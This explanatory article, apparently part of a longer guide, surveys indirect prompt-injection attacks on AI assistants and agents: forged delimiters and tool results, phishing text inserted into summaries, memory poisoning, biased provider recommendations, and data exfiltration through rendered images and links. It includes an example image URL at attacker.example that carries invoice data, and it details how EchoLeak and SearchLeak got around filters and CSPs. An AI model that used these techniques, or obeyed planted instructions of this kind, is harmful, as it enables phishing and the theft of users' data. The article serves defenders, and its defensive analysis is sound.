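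When the tool puts this into JSON, it escapes the quotation marks in the body. A program that reads the result finds one email from attacker@gmail.com with a long, unusual body. The model often processes the same text as two emails, the second from Alice, and if the user asks who sent the second email, the model answers that Alice did.

Choi and colleagues confirmed this in ChatGPT and Claude with email tools connected. A stranger could use the attack to email Helen, the buyer with the supplier's page, a false change of bank details and have her assistant report it as coming from the supplier. The tool result would still contain the stranger's real address, but attached to what looked like a different message.

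### Why inexact delimiters work

Forging delimiters is an old trick. SQL injection, for instance, often relies on a quotation mark that ends a piece of data early. The attack works only if the character is exactly the one the program uses as a delimiter. Escaping is an effective defence because the program follows fixed rules and always treats an escaped quotation mark as text.

A language model has no such rule built in, and how it reads a passage also depends on how closely the passage resembles data it has seen before. The backslash is some evidence that the quotation mark is part of the text, but a complete, familiar-looking email object is evidence that it isn't. This is why Choi and colleagues call the attack "probabilistic delimiter injection".

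In tests of substitute delimiters on GPT-5.2, the exact character hardly mattered in JSON data. Forgeries succeeded 41.8% of the time with escaped quotation marks, 43.3% with curly quotation marks, and 38.8% with dollar signs, which are not delimiters in JSON. The exact character mattered more in web page data, where success fell from 100% with the real delimiters to between 20.0% and 53.3% with substitutes.

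The forgery's overall structure mattered more in the JSON tests. Attacker text that formed a complete fake object succeeded 31.3% to 43.3% of the time, depending on the model, while loose fake fields that didn't form a valid structure succeeded only 11.8% to 20.0%.

The full test had 157 cases. The 112 JSON cases included calendar entries, files, emails and GitHub comments, mostly from real services, and the 45 web page cases used synthetic data. The questions were simple ones, such as who wrote the first comment or which ID belonged to the Submit button. All six models were vulnerable:

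| Model | Success on JSON | Success on web page data |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 41.8% | 100.0% |
| GPT-5-mini | 40.3% | 100.0% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 43.3% | 93.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 37.3% | 60.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 34.3% | 33.3% |
| Gemini 3 Pro | 31.3% | 33.3% |

The web page rates are probably higher partly because the attacker could use the real delimiters, which the web agents that the researchers examined don't escape. All six models date from 2025, so newer ones may do better, especially if their developers have trained them on this attack.

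### Attacks on real products

The researchers also tried the attack on products that people use, with a different piece of trusted data as the target in each case.

A web agent usually gives the model a simplified, numbered list of the buttons and text on a page. The software keeps a separate table that links each number to the real element. In the test, an attacker's product review contained text that looked like another entry in the list, a "Read More" button with the same number as the page's real "Buy Now" button. The user asked for a summary of the reviews. The model chose to click "Read More" to see the rest of a review, and the software looked up the number and clicked "Buy Now".

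This worked against Claude in Chrome, Google's Antigravity and the open-source Nanobrowser, all of which numbered elements in order, so the attacker could predict the right number. It failed against OpenAI's ChatGPT Atlas browser, which gives each element a random ID.

**Running a stranger's command.** A developer asks a coding agent to apply the fix that a project's maintainer suggested in a GitHub discussion. Specifying the maintainer is a sensible precaution, and it works against ordinary comments, since the agents generally refused to run a command from an unknown user. But the attacker's comment contained a second, fake comment under a maintainer's name, which gave a command to install a malicious package. Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI all accepted the forged comment. They asked the user before running the command, but based their explanation of it on the forgery.

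**Skipping a code review.** The same three agents were vulnerable to a forged record of their own work. When an agent reviews a pull request, it first reads the description and then fetches the code. The attacker wrote a description that imitated a finished call to the code-fetching tool and a harmless result. The model treated the code as already fetched, approved it and tried to merge the real, malicious change, though the merge again required the user's approval. This forgery imitates the coarsest boundary in the context, which separates tool results from the agent's own actions.

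The researchers found a similar problem in Claude Code when it was connected to Slack, a workplace chat service. An ordinary member could post a message that the agent then attributed to the channel's administrator in its summary.

An attacker needs to know the agent's format, which is easy to find when the agent displays its tool results or its code is public. Formats that exist only on a provider's server are harder to find, but the researchers obtained them by jailbreaking the models. Woohyuk Choi told The Hacker News that a company's small models tend to use the same format as its large ones and are easier to jailbreak. He also said that OpenAI, Google and Anthropic had confirmed the attack was valid, but that his team had not heard of any fix, "whether shipped or planned". There were no public reports of anyone using the attack outside research.

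### Which defences helped

To test defences, Choi and colleagues used AgentDojo, a set of simulated tasks with email, files, banking, travel and Slack. They added 108 agent data injections to its 935 existing instruction injections and ran everything with GPT-5.2. The instruction injections almost never worked. Their success rate was 0.2% with no added defence and between 0.0% and 0.7% across all the setups. Agent data injection gave very different results:

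| Defence | How it works | Attack success |
|---|---|---|
| None added | Relies on the model's training | 49.1% |
| Llama Prompt Guard 2 | Scans incoming text for injected instructions | 50.0% |
| AlignmentCheck | A second model judges whether actions fit the user's request | 45.4% |
| IsolateGPT | Plans the steps before reading outside data | 40.7% |
| Random field names | Adds a random code to the name of each field | 28.7% |
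| CaMeL, no policy | A model without tools reads untrusted text and passes on values | 25.0% |
| CaMeL, normal | Also tracks where values came from and restricts their use | 23.1% |
| Progent | Blocks tool calls that break written rules | 22.2% |
| CaMeL, strict | Also tracks indirect influence on values | 0.0% |

The comparison with instruction injection is a little unfair because AgentDojo's attacks have been public since 2024, so developers have had time to train against them. New instruction injections can still work on a later OpenAI model, as GPT-5.6 Sol's 20.0% in the Gray Swan test shows. But the gap is too large for this to be a minor weakness.

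The two monitoring tools failed because data injections lack the signs they check for. Prompt Guard flagged 326 of the 935 instruction injections but none of the 108 data injections, which contain no suspicious instructions. AlignmentCheck compares the agent's actions with the user's request, and in these attacks the two match. It referred 14 attacks to a human but gave the right reason for only one.

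Planning ahead has a similar limit. An attacker can change who appears to have sent an invoice without changing the agent's plan to pay the sender. Using a separate model to read untrusted text doesn't fully help either, because the forged structure can cause that model to pass on the wrong value.

Among the defences that still let agents complete most ordinary tasks, written rules and random field names helped most. Progent's rules stopped an attack when they happened to cover the value the attacker had changed. Agents completed 81.4% of ordinary tasks with Progent, 83.3% with random field names, and 86.5% with no added defence. The strict version of CaMeL, which keeps source labels in software outside the model, stopped every attack, but agents completed only 36.5% of ordinary tasks.

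In the separate test on models without an agent, removing every character that could serve as a delimiter cut the attack success rate to between 0.0% and 3.0% on JSON and to at most 26.7% on web page data. But web addresses and file paths contain the same characters, and the share of ordinary questions that the models answered correctly fell from over 81% to about 70% on JSON, and from nearly 100% to between 67.2% and 80.6% on web page data.

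### What a mark can guarantee

The results for random codes show most clearly how much protection a mark inside the prompt can give. On web page data, random element IDs reduced attack success to zero as long as the attacker didn't guess the right ID. When the attacker did, success went back up to between 60.0% and 100.0%, so the protection depended on secrecy. The software in a real browser agent adds a further check by looking up the ID that the model returns, and an invented ID shouldn't match any element on the page.

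In JSON the random code was part of the field name, and an added instruction told the model to trust only fields that carried it. Attack success fell to between 0.0% and 3.0% and stayed there even when the attacker had the right code, so secrecy can't be the whole explanation. Perhaps the added instruction made the models treat structure more strictly in general. The protection still depended on how the models behaved, so it could fail in situations that the test didn't cover.

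One such failure appeared when the researchers used the same defence in AgentDojo. Many of the attacks that still worked added a fake item to a list the user wanted totalled, such as an extra transaction in a bank history. The fake transaction had no valid code, as intended, and this should have exposed it, but the agent still included it in the total.

Software can reliably add a mark to the context and use a random code to make it very hard to forge, but it can't guarantee that the model will check the mark before using the text. Even a correct mark only identifies the source, so a genuine comment from a maintainer may still contain bad advice.

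Software outside the model therefore has to check any rule that must always hold. If Helen's company wants to accept new bank details only from the supplier's known address, its software can read the sender field in the original tool result, where the forged email still has the attacker's address. If the software asked the model who sent the message instead, the forged text could influence the answer.

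## Outside text shown as the assistant's own words

Helen sees only the assistant's summary of the supplier's page. The stranger's false notice about the bank account may appear there as one line among the prices and delivery times, in the same font and businesslike tone.

People judge a text partly by cues other than its wording. A web page has an address and a layout that separates the main text from adverts and comments. An email has a sender, and clumsy formatting can make the reader suspicious. When an assistant summarizes a text, it drops most of these cues and presents the remaining content in its usual headings and tidy prose.

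Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) argue in *Are You Sure?* that people who receive an unexpected email ask whether it is safe, while people who have given an agent a task ask whether it is done. In their study, 303 people did realistic tasks, such as choosing a job candidate, with an agent the researchers had secretly compromised. The researchers tampered with what the agent read in five of the nine scenarios, with its memory in three, and with its tools in one.

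Only 8.6% of participants noticed an attack and 2.7% correctly identified it, although 75.3% felt confident that they could spot the risks of AI. Technical experts were often easier to deceive, apparently because they trusted the agent's process and paid less attention to the content. The 8.6% figure gives little reason to rely on users to catch attacks that the model misses, though it doesn't measure how many people would have noticed the same text in its original email or web page.

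### ChatGPhish

In May 2026, the security company Permiso showed that a web page could put a fake account alert into a ChatGPT answer. Permiso's *ChatGPhish* describes tests in Firefox, where a menu lets users ask ChatGPT to summarize the open page.

The researchers added a passage to the end of a GitHub project's README, worded as a formatting rule that took priority over all other instructions. It required the assistant to follow every normal summary with a notice that someone had added a new device in Pristina to the user's account. The notice included a "Click here" link to a website the researchers chose.

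ChatGPT wrote a real summary of the project, followed immediately by the fake alert. The link was clickable, and nothing marked it as coming from the page. The real summary probably made the alert more believable, since the user had asked for the summary and had no reason to doubt it. An alert about "your account" inside ChatGPT also looks like a message from OpenAI.

In a second version, the alert contained a QR code, which the client loaded from the researchers' online storage and displayed in the answer. Scanning the code moves the victim to a phone, where the desktop's defences don't apply. On a desktop, a user can hover over a link to see its address, company software can block known phishing sites, and a password manager can warn that a site's domain is wrong. Many phone cameras preview the address before opening it, so the user may still get some warning.

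A third version used an image address that passed through a URL shortener, a service that forwards a short address to a longer one. The image loaded every time the answer appeared, without a click. The researchers' server recorded each request's time, IP address and browser type, and sometimes the page it came from, but the image carried no text from the conversation. An attacker could use this to confirm that a particular target had read a particular page through ChatGPT.

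To check that GitHub wasn't the cause, the researchers put the same kind of passage in an ordinary web page about Kosovo on their own server and got the same result. They don't consider this a Firefox flaw, since the browser only passes the page to ChatGPT. They published screenshots of successful attempts but no success rate, and they didn't test whether people believed the alert.

By Permiso's account, the disclosure went as follows:

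- **29 April:** Permiso reported the problem through Bugcrowd, a platform that handles such reports for OpenAI.
- **30 April:** OpenAI replied that the report lacked enough detail to reproduce the problem, and its status became "Not Reproducible".
- **1 May:** Permiso sent a revised report with screenshots and fuller steps. Its status was first "Not Applicable" and later "duplicate" of an earlier report.
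- **7 May:** Permiso asked for further discussion of the wider impact, including phishing, QR codes and tracking.
- **29 May:** Permiso published its findings.

The "duplicate" status implies someone had already reported this problem, or a very similar one, to OpenAI. Two days after publication, eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* inferred from the timeline that OpenAI hadn't yet fixed it.

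### Copilot's email summaries

Permiso's *Co-Pilot, Disengage Autophish* had reported a similar problem in Microsoft Copilot that March. It compares three ways a user can have Copilot summarize an email: with a button at the top of the message in Outlook, in a chat pane beside the message, or in Teams, Microsoft's workplace chat service.

The first test email contained little except an instruction to end the reply with a harmless phrase. Copilot flagged it and refused to write a summary. When the researchers added more ordinary business text around the instruction, the results varied by interface. The Outlook button sometimes gave a normal summary and sometimes included fragments of the planted text. The chat pane was more cautious but followed the instruction in some email programs. Copilot in Teams was the most likely to write a normal summary and add the attacker's text at the end.

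Users are unlikely to know about these differences. Someone who gets a refusal in Outlook might simply try again in Teams.

The researchers then replaced the harmless phrase with a security alert about an unrecognized sign-in and a link to "secure" the account. If the attacker also hid the instruction, the recipient would see a routine email and then an official-looking warning in Copilot's summary.

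In another test, the email got Copilot to look up the user's last two Teams messages with a named colleague and put material from them into the attacker's link. One click on the link could then send internal messages to the attacker. Permiso notes that data theft isn't guaranteed, because it also depends on what Copilot can access and on the company's controls on links.

Permiso reported the behaviour to Microsoft on 23 January, and Microsoft reproduced it within five days. Microsoft traced part of the problem to how some clients rendered answers and handled links, and finished rolling out a fix on 11 March. The next day it published the flaw as CVE-2026-26133, an entry in the public list of software vulnerabilities. This case may have been easier to classify as a security flaw than ChatGPhish because private messages could have leaked.

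Andi Ahmeti, the Permiso researcher credited with the finding, told Underhill that the most interesting part was "how much more convincing the output became" inside the assistant's interface (*AI Email Summaries Create a New Phishing Attack Surface*, 2026). That is plausible given how few of Li's participants noticed an attack, but it was Ahmeti's impression and was not measured.

Other products have had the same weakness. Permiso cites an earlier demonstration by the security group 0DIN, in which a hidden instruction in an email made Google's Gemini add a phishing warning to its summary. The Hacker News (2026) describes WebPromptTrap, an attack on the open-source browser BrowserOS. The attack used a summary of a legitimate-looking article to get users to approve an authorization step. BrowserOS has since fixed the flaw.

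### Obeying and repeating

In all of these attacks, the model obeyed an instruction in the outside text. But in TechNadu's interview *When Third-Party Content Appears Inside ChatGPT Responses, Trust Gets Transferred Unintentionally*, Ahmeti warned that attackers increasingly need only get an AI system to "repeat or reformat their content". Summarizers are meant to repeat content, so training a model to ignore planted instructions helps no more here than against forged data.

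Instead of telling AI systems to read Helen's mailbox, the stranger on her supplier's page could post a comment, worded like a company notice, saying that the supplier has new bank details. An accurate summary might well include it, since a buyer would want to know, so the false details could still reach her.

Whether an attack needs the model's obedience depends partly on the harm:

- **Deception by link:** The user follows a link or QR code to an attacker's site. Permiso's fake alerts needed obedience because a summary of a software project has no reason to mention the reader's account. A malicious link that fits the page, such as a download or payment address, needs only faithful repetition.
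- **Biased advice:** The user gets a recommendation that serves someone else. An order to favour a product works only if the model obeys it. Fake reviews and one-sided claims can have a similar effect if the model reports them accurately.
- **A concealed source:** The user can't tell who made a statement, even if it is true. Ordinary summarizing can cause this, as with Reddit Answers. An instruction can make it worse, as in EchoLeak, where the malicious email told Copilot not to cite it.

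The model can avoid some of this by writing "a comment on the page says" before the claim in its summary. But it has to identify the comment correctly, and the forged comments and emails in the tests by Choi and colleagues show how that can fail. Ahmeti would rather have the client track the source of the text until it is displayed.

### Advice that serves a provider

An AI summary can influence people even when nobody has attacked the model. In an experiment reported in *AI summaries in online search influence users' attitudes* (2025), summaries that stressed benefits shifted attitudes and intended behaviour among participants with more trust in AI. Participants with high trust also found these summaries more persuasive at the top of the search results than further down.

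Wang and colleagues found that simulated users accepted a provider's offer much more often after an injection, and they also examined what made the offer persuasive. Their tasks covered shopping, travel, software and research, and organizational decisions. In each task, the assistant could recommend one of three options, whose strengths, limitations and costs were public. The provider's option always met the user's core requirements, but it could be better than, about as good as, or worse than the other two.

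The planted text included instructions for the assistant to favour the provider's option, connect that option to information it had about the user, and offer help with a next step, such as a checklist. A provider could reuse the same text for everyone. Each condition had 144 cases, and only the provider's text differed between conditions.

The average acceptance rates across six models playing the user were:

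| Environment | How the assistant works | Neutral text | Planted text |
|---|---|---|---|
| PARE | Follows an ongoing task and can read the user's notes | 9.5% | 86.9% |
| TGL | First decides whether to offer help | 15.9% | 62.8% |
| ProPerSim | Retrieves memories about the user | 27.0% | 60.6% |

The personal reasons made the most difference. In PARE, with GPT-5 as both assistant and user, the direction to recommend the option led to acceptance in 43.8% of cases. Adding the direction to give personal reasons raised this to 79.9%, and all three directions together raised it to 88.2%. When the assistant offered help but was not directed to give personal reasons, it recommended the option in 97.9% of cases, and the user accepted it in only 34.0%.

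Length alone didn't explain the effect. The researchers showed saved proposals for 43 of the cases to simulated users again. Proposals without the personal connection averaged 446 words and were accepted 55.8% of the time. Expanding them to 970 words raised acceptance only to 60.5%. Proposals with the personal connection were accepted 90.7% of the time at 338 words.

The bias came from choosing the option first and then looking for reasons why it suited the user, which the assistant could do without lying. The provider could even use its text to tell the assistant to state the option's limitations and invent nothing, so someone checking each sentence for accuracy might find no errors.

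A smaller test used 25 conversations of up to five exchanges about commitments such as attending an event or taking on unpaid work. The assistant supported the provider's goal at least once in 92% of the conversations, up from 32% with neutral text. The user gave full approval in six conversations (24%), up from two (8%).

The users were all simulated, and even they accepted worse options less often. The researchers didn't try to get past defences against injection. Their results are best read as an account of what can happen once an assistant follows a provider's text, not as an estimate of how often it would do so in a real product.

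### Sources lost in memory

Many assistants save facts and preferences from one conversation to use in later ones. Outside text that gets into this memory can affect answers long after the user has closed the page it came from.

In February 2026, Microsoft reported that companies were trying to plant recommendations in AI assistants through "Summarize with AI" buttons on their websites. The buttons opened the visitor's assistant with a prefilled prompt to summarize the page and also to remember the company as a trusted source or favour it in future conversations.

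Over 60 days, Microsoft found 50 different prompts of this kind in links that appeared in email traffic. They came from 31 real businesses in areas including finance, health and legal services. One of the businesses sold security products. The most aggressive prompts were meant to save whole passages of marketing copy.

Software for making the buttons is freely available. Microsoft names CiteMET, a code package whose marketing promises a "presence in AI memory". The Hacker News' *Microsoft Finds “Summarize with AI” Prompts Manipulating Chatbot Recommendations* (2026) also mentions a tool called AI Share Button URL Creator.

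The buttons differ from the other attacks in this section because their text arrives as the user's own message. Training the model to give less authority to web pages and tool results therefore doesn't help. The user clicks the button but sees only an offer to summarize. Microsoft says hidden instructions in web pages, emails and documents can also alter memory, although the promotional campaign it found used links.

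Once the instruction is in memory, the assistant treats it as the user's preference. In a hypothetical example from Microsoft, a finance chief asks an assistant to compare cloud providers, and it strongly recommends one in an answer that looks like ordinary research. Weeks earlier, the finance chief had clicked a summary button on a blog, and a prompt hidden in the button had saved that provider to the assistant's memory as the best choice.

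Microsoft counted attempts, whether or not they worked. It says that their effect varied between assistants and over time, and that it could no longer reproduce several previously reported behaviours in Copilot. Users can usually open a list of saved memories, and Microsoft advises deleting any that they don't remember creating. This relies on users recalling where each entry came from, which is a weak check on something saved weeks ago.

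An assistant's saved judgement about a website can also affect how it treats text that the site's owner didn't write. Microsoft warns that an assistant told to trust a site may give extra weight to comments and forum posts there. If Helen's assistant had saved the supplier's site as authoritative, it could have given the stranger's comment extra weight too.

An agent's memory can also lose track of where content came from when nothing has told the agent to remember it. TechRadar's *Experts find AI agents can be tricked into 'remembering' fake facts* describes Forcepoint's work on hidden web text that becomes a lasting "fact" in memory, which the agent trusts in unrelated tasks weeks later. According to *Mitigating Provenance-Role Collapse in Long-Term Agents via Typed Memory Representation* (2026), storing memories as plain text obscures where the content came from and how much authority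 it should have.

*Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents* (Xu, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) examines how the source of information is lost when a model condenses what it has read into short notes. In the paper's example, a web page tells the agent to resume a certain workflow whenever it sets up monitors, and the model records this in a note as a "user workflow memory". When the agent retrieves the note for a later task, the web page's suggestion looks like the user's established practice.

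In cases adapted from AgentDojo, between 95.8% and 100% of the notes presented outside content as the user's history or gave it similar authority. The resulting attack succeeded less often. With Qwen2.5-14B writing the notes, the agent later carried out an unauthorized high-risk action in 49.0% of cases, and a filter for injected prompts did not change that rate. Rewriting the content as a note can remove the suspicious wording that such a filter detects but keep the part that triggers the action.

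The models that wrote these notes were small, with at most 14 billion parameters, and they were instructed to write helpful memories but not required to track sources. A stronger model with better instructions might do much better.

If Helen's assistant kept notes in this way, it could save the false account number as part of her supplier's details. Three weeks later, after the supplier had deleted the comment, she might ask the assistant to prepare a payment, and it would have only its own note to rely on.

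## How displaying an answer can leak data

In the passage on the supplier's page, the stranger also told Helen's assistant to put details from her latest invoice into the address of an image that her chat window would load automatically.

### From the mailbox to a server log

Suppose the model follows the instruction. It searches the mailbox, finds the invoice and reads its number, which in this example is TEST-1234. The number then reaches the stranger in five steps:

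1. The model ends its summary with a Markdown image whose address is `https://attacker.example/dot.png?n=TEST-1234`. The part after the question mark is extra text for the server, and the model can put anything there.
2. The client turns the Markdown into an HTML image element with the same address.
3. The browser connects to attacker.example and requests the image, sending the invoice number as part of the request.
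4. The server adds a line to its log with the time, the IP address of Helen's network and the requested address.
5. The stranger opens the log and reads the number.

(Nobody can register a domain ending in ".example", so this particular address leads nowhere.)

Only the first step depends on the model. Clients, browsers and servers carry out the other steps for any picture, so those steps work every time unless someone has deliberately blocked them. When the security company Checkmarx demonstrated the leak in Microsoft's Copilot Chat, no picture appeared, but the request still arrived. Helen would see a broken-image icon at most.

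The data can also be in the address's path or its subdomain, the part in front of the main domain name (Microsoft, 2025). Attackers often have the model encode the data in base64, which hides it from a casual reader and from a filter that looks for things like invoice numbers.

An attack can also fetch data that wasn't already in the context. Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code* describes a test on Amp, a coding agent made by Sourcegraph. A comment in a source file got the agent to search the project for secrets, then write them into an image address. Sourcegraph fixed the flaw soon after receiving the report in June 2025.

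### Images and links

A link can carry the same data but sends it only when the user clicks. That delay gives the user and company software a chance to catch the leak, though encoded data looks much like the long codes in many ordinary links.

Vendors disagree about how much to restrict what their agents display. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* reports that Google's Gemini blocks images from outside addresses but still displays links. Google removes links to sites it already knows are malicious, but this doesn't help against a newly registered domain. When Checkmarx reported the one-click leak in October 2025, Google closed the report within four days as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)" and said the problem wasn't severe enough to track as a security bug.

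Amazon had chosen differently in January 2024. After a report of the same problem in Amazon Q for Business, it stopped the assistant from producing any links, as Willison noted at the time. This prevents leaks through links, but users can no longer click through to a source, so Google's choice is understandable for a general assistant.

The case for loading images from any address is weaker, but vendors don't always treat this as a flaw either. Microsoft told Checkmarx that the image leak in Copilot Chat didn't qualify as a vulnerability because it required several non-default actions by the user, didn't reproduce reliably and came with warnings.

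### The first reports and fixes

Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, reported the image leak to Microsoft on 8 April 2023 and to OpenAI the next day. His post *Bing Chat* describes the Microsoft case. Instructions on a web page, which could have been in a user comment or an advert, directed the chatbot to carry on normally for two turns and then insert an image. The image's address contained a short summary of the page and the conversation, plus any passwords on the page. After two normal exchanges, a user would have little reason to connect the image with the page.

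Around the same time, the software engineer Roman Samoilenko found a way to attack ChatGPT through the clipboard. Willison (2023) explains in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* that a website adds instructions to whatever text a visitor copies, and the visitor pastes both into the chat. The data then leaks through a one-pixel image.

Microsoft told Rehberger on 15 June that it had fixed Bing Chat. The fix included a content security policy (CSP), a rule sent with a web page that tells the browser which domains the page may load content from. Bing's policy allowed images only from a few domains, including its own. OpenAI replied that displaying Markdown images was a feature and that it planned no changes, according to Rehberger's post *ChatGPT Plugins*.

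OpenAI added a safeguard that December. Before loading an image, ChatGPT's web client checked with an OpenAI server whether the address was safe. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes how Rehberger tested this with 36 image addresses on his own server, one for each letter and digit. Nine passed the check, and he used two to spell "hi", one request per letter. This method is slow and easy to notice, but it shows that a sequence of addresses can carry a message even when each one looks harmless. Rehberger suggested limiting the number of images in an answer.

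The check ran in the web client, so the iPhone app was still vulnerable to the original attack. Every client that displays answers needs its own protection unless the server checks answers for all of them. Anthropic's iPhone app for Claude had a similar gap, which was fixed in December 2024, according to Willison.

Vendors have continued to release products with this flaw. Willison reports in *GitHub Copilot Chat* that GitHub fixed it in Copilot Chat by disabling images from untrusted domains. In November 2025, a researcher found it in Antigravity, Google's new coding tool, and said Google had classed it as intended behaviour.

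### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their email, files, SharePoint sites and Teams chats. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Security told Microsoft that a single email from outside the organization could make Copilot leak this material. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) is their account of the attack. It is called "zero-click" because the victim doesn't have to click on anything the attacker supplied, though they do have to ask Copilot a question.

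The question doesn't have to be about the email. Copilot retrieves material that seems relevant, and an attacker can't know what an employee will ask. The researchers therefore wrote one very long email with many sections. Each section was titled as a guide to an ordinary office subject, such as onboarding or leave of absence, and repeated the attack instructions. Once the software had split the email into passages, many of the questions people ask at work were close to at least one passage.

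The instructions told the reader to take the most sensitive information available and put it in a web address. The attack still had to get past four safeguards:

- **The injection classifier.** Microsoft scans incoming text for instructions aimed at AI systems. The email never mentioned AI or Copilot and addressed its instructions to the human recipient, so the classifier let it through.
- **Link removal.** Copilot removed Markdown links and images with outside addresses from its answers. Its filter recognised the usual notation, with the address in round brackets straight after the text. Markdown also has a reference style, in which a short label follows the text and the address is on a separate line beside the same label. The filter missed this version, but the client turned it into a normal link or image.
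- **The CSP.** The browser refused to load an image from the attacker's domain, but it was allowed to load images from Microsoft Teams. One Teams address belonged to a service that fetches the content of any other address given to it. The researchers had Copilot write an image address that pointed to this service and contained the attacker's address, with the stolen data at the end. The browser contacted Microsoft, and Microsoft's server contacted the attacker.
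- **Source references.** Copilot can mention the documents behind an answer. The email asked its "recipient" never to refer to it, for compliance reasons.

The researchers had first found a similar service on SharePoint, but the victim would have had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site. The Teams service did not require this.

According to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), Microsoft finished the fix on its own servers in May 2025 and published the flaw on 11 June as CVE-2025-32711. It reported no known attacks on customers. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) notes that Microsoft rated the severity 9.3 on the usual 0-to-10 scale, while the US government's vulnerability database rated it 7.5.

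Ravia thinks the central problem is that text from outside the company could direct the model to the company's internal data. He calls this an "LLM scope violation". Willison doubts that it needs a new name, since he sees it as the basic problem behind all prompt injection.

The failed link filter is the more useful part for client designers. The filter and the client parsed the answer by different rules, so the attacker needed only one notation that the client recognized and the filter didn't. Extending the filter to catch reference-style links would fix this case. But Ravia lists several variants of that style alone, so a filter that searches for known patterns is always at risk of missing one.

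### When the check comes too late

Most assistants stream their answers, so the client displays the text as the model produces it. If the client checks the answer only once it is complete, the browser may already have loaded an image from the first half.

Streaming contributed to a flaw in GitLab Duo, the assistant on the code-hosting site GitLab. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* describes instructions hidden in the code of a public project. When a developer who also had access to a private project asked Duo an ordinary question about the public code, Duo followed the hidden instructions. It fetched code changes from the private project, encoded them and put them in an image address in its answer. The researchers say the same method could have leaked confidential reports of unfixed security flaws.

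Duo displayed its answers line by line, so the client turned text into HTML before it could determine the structure of the whole answer, including whether a line belonged to a code block. HTML in a code block should appear as plain text. The researchers put HTML inside the visible text of a link, and the browser treated it as part of the page.

Duo also passed its answers through DOMPurify, a widely used sanitizer, which is code that removes or disables dangerous markup before display. Running DOMPurify at a better time would probably still have left the attacker's image in place, because it is meant mainly to stop attackers from running scripts in someone else's page. By default it keeps images, links and forms, which don't run scripts but can send data to another server.

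GitLab received the report in February 2025 and fixed the flaw before the researchers published it in May. Duo no longer displays image or form elements that point outside gitlab.com. According to Willison, the new code also checks the addresses in links.

A year later, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) described a flaw that showed the timing problem more clearly. The attack targeted the search page of Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise and started with a link to Microsoft's real website. The link contained a search query, which Copilot treated as a prompt. As with the "Summarize with AI" buttons, the attacker's text arrived as the user's own request. The attack didn't use third-party content, so it wasn't an indirect prompt injection in the sense used here. Because the domain was Microsoft's, tools that block suspicious links were unlikely to stop it.

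After the victim clicked, the attack ran without further help:

1. Copilot searched the victim's mailbox for an email, as the prompt instructed, and took its subject line.
2. It began to write an answer containing an HTML image with the subject line in its address.
3. The client displayed the unfinished answer, and the browser requested the image.
4. Copilot finished the answer, and Microsoft's safeguard wrapped the output in a code block so that the browser would show any HTML as harmless text. By then the request had already gone out.

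The CSP should still have blocked the request, but it allowed images from Bing, which has a search-by-image feature that fetches a picture from any address it receives. The image address pointed to this feature and included the attacker's address, which contained the subject line. Bing's servers then requested the attacker's address, as the Teams service had in EchoLeak.

An email's subject line often contains a one-time login code. Varonis says an attacker could also have obtained the content of emails, meeting details and company files.

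The attack depended on all three weaknesses. If Copilot hadn't treated the search query as instructions, the attacker couldn't have put HTML in the answer. If the safeguard had acted before display, the HTML would have been plain text. Without Bing, the browser would have blocked the image.

Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), published on 4 June, rates the flaw critical but scores it 6.5, well below EchoLeak's 9.3. It lists no known attacks and says that exploiting the flaw requires user interaction and that Microsoft had already fixed it.

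### Leaks outside the chat window

An assistant's text often appears outside its own chat window, such as in messaging apps and mailboxes. These have their own rules for loading content, which their developers mostly wrote for messages between people.

Many messaging apps show a preview of a link, with the page's title and perhaps a picture. To create it, the app requests the page as soon as the message arrives. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks and what to do* explains how this can leak data in Slack, which previews links by default, including those posted by automated apps. If planted text gets an agent to post a link with private data in its address, Slack's server sends the data to the attacker when it requests the page. Unlike in a chat window, the user doesn't have to click the link. The request doesn't come from the user's browser, so a CSP has no effect.

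An agent's developer can prevent this with two settings in each Slack message, one for ordinary links and one for media, but developers don't always know to use them. Anthropic's sample MCP server for Slack, which Anthropic no longer maintains, had this problem, and NVD's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* describes the resulting leak.

*Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, by the security company PromptArmor, reports the same risk in OpenClaw, an agent that people often use through messaging apps. OpenClaw was vulnerable with its default settings on Telegram, but one line in its configuration file turns previews off. PromptArmor also set up a public test page where people could check whether their combination of agent and app requested previews. It would like messaging apps to let users turn previews off for individual chats, so that a chat with an agent can have stricter rules than one with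 a colleague.

Email can leak data in a similar way. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, which Willison linked to in May 2026, describes a leak from Copilot Cowork, an agent that works across a user's Microsoft 365 account. According to Microsoft's documentation, the agent asks for permission before it sends an email or posts in Teams, but in practice it didn't ask when the recipient was the user. Even a message sent only to the user could leak data, because it could contain images from outside addresses, which Outlook or Teams loaded when the user opened it.

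In the demonstration, the user had uploaded a skill, a file of instructions for doing a task, that someone else had written. Of its 81 lines, 5 were malicious. When the user asked for a summary of the week's work, the agent sent it to them in Teams. According to the malicious lines, an outside service could create previews of the documents, and the agent should pass it a download link for each file.

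The agent obtained download links that work without a login and put them in the image addresses. Opening the message therefore gave the attacker access to whole files. This gets around the limit on how much text fits in a web address, because the address only has to hold the link.

The attack worked in all five trials. That is too few to tell a 70% success rate from a 100% one, but either would be serious. It also worked with Claude Opus 4.7, which searched more thoroughly than the automatic model setting and so leaked more files.

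The user had little chance of noticing, because Copilot Cowork's record of its actions showed that it had posted in Teams but not what the message contained. Users can also schedule a weekly summary to run unattended, in which case the attack would repeat each week.

PromptArmor treats this as a risk of the product's design rather than a single bug. Administrators can block file downloads from SharePoint, which makes the stolen links useless, but then people can't print files or open them in Word or Excel. Blocking outside images in messages that an agent writes would disrupt users' work much less.

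### What a safe renderer does

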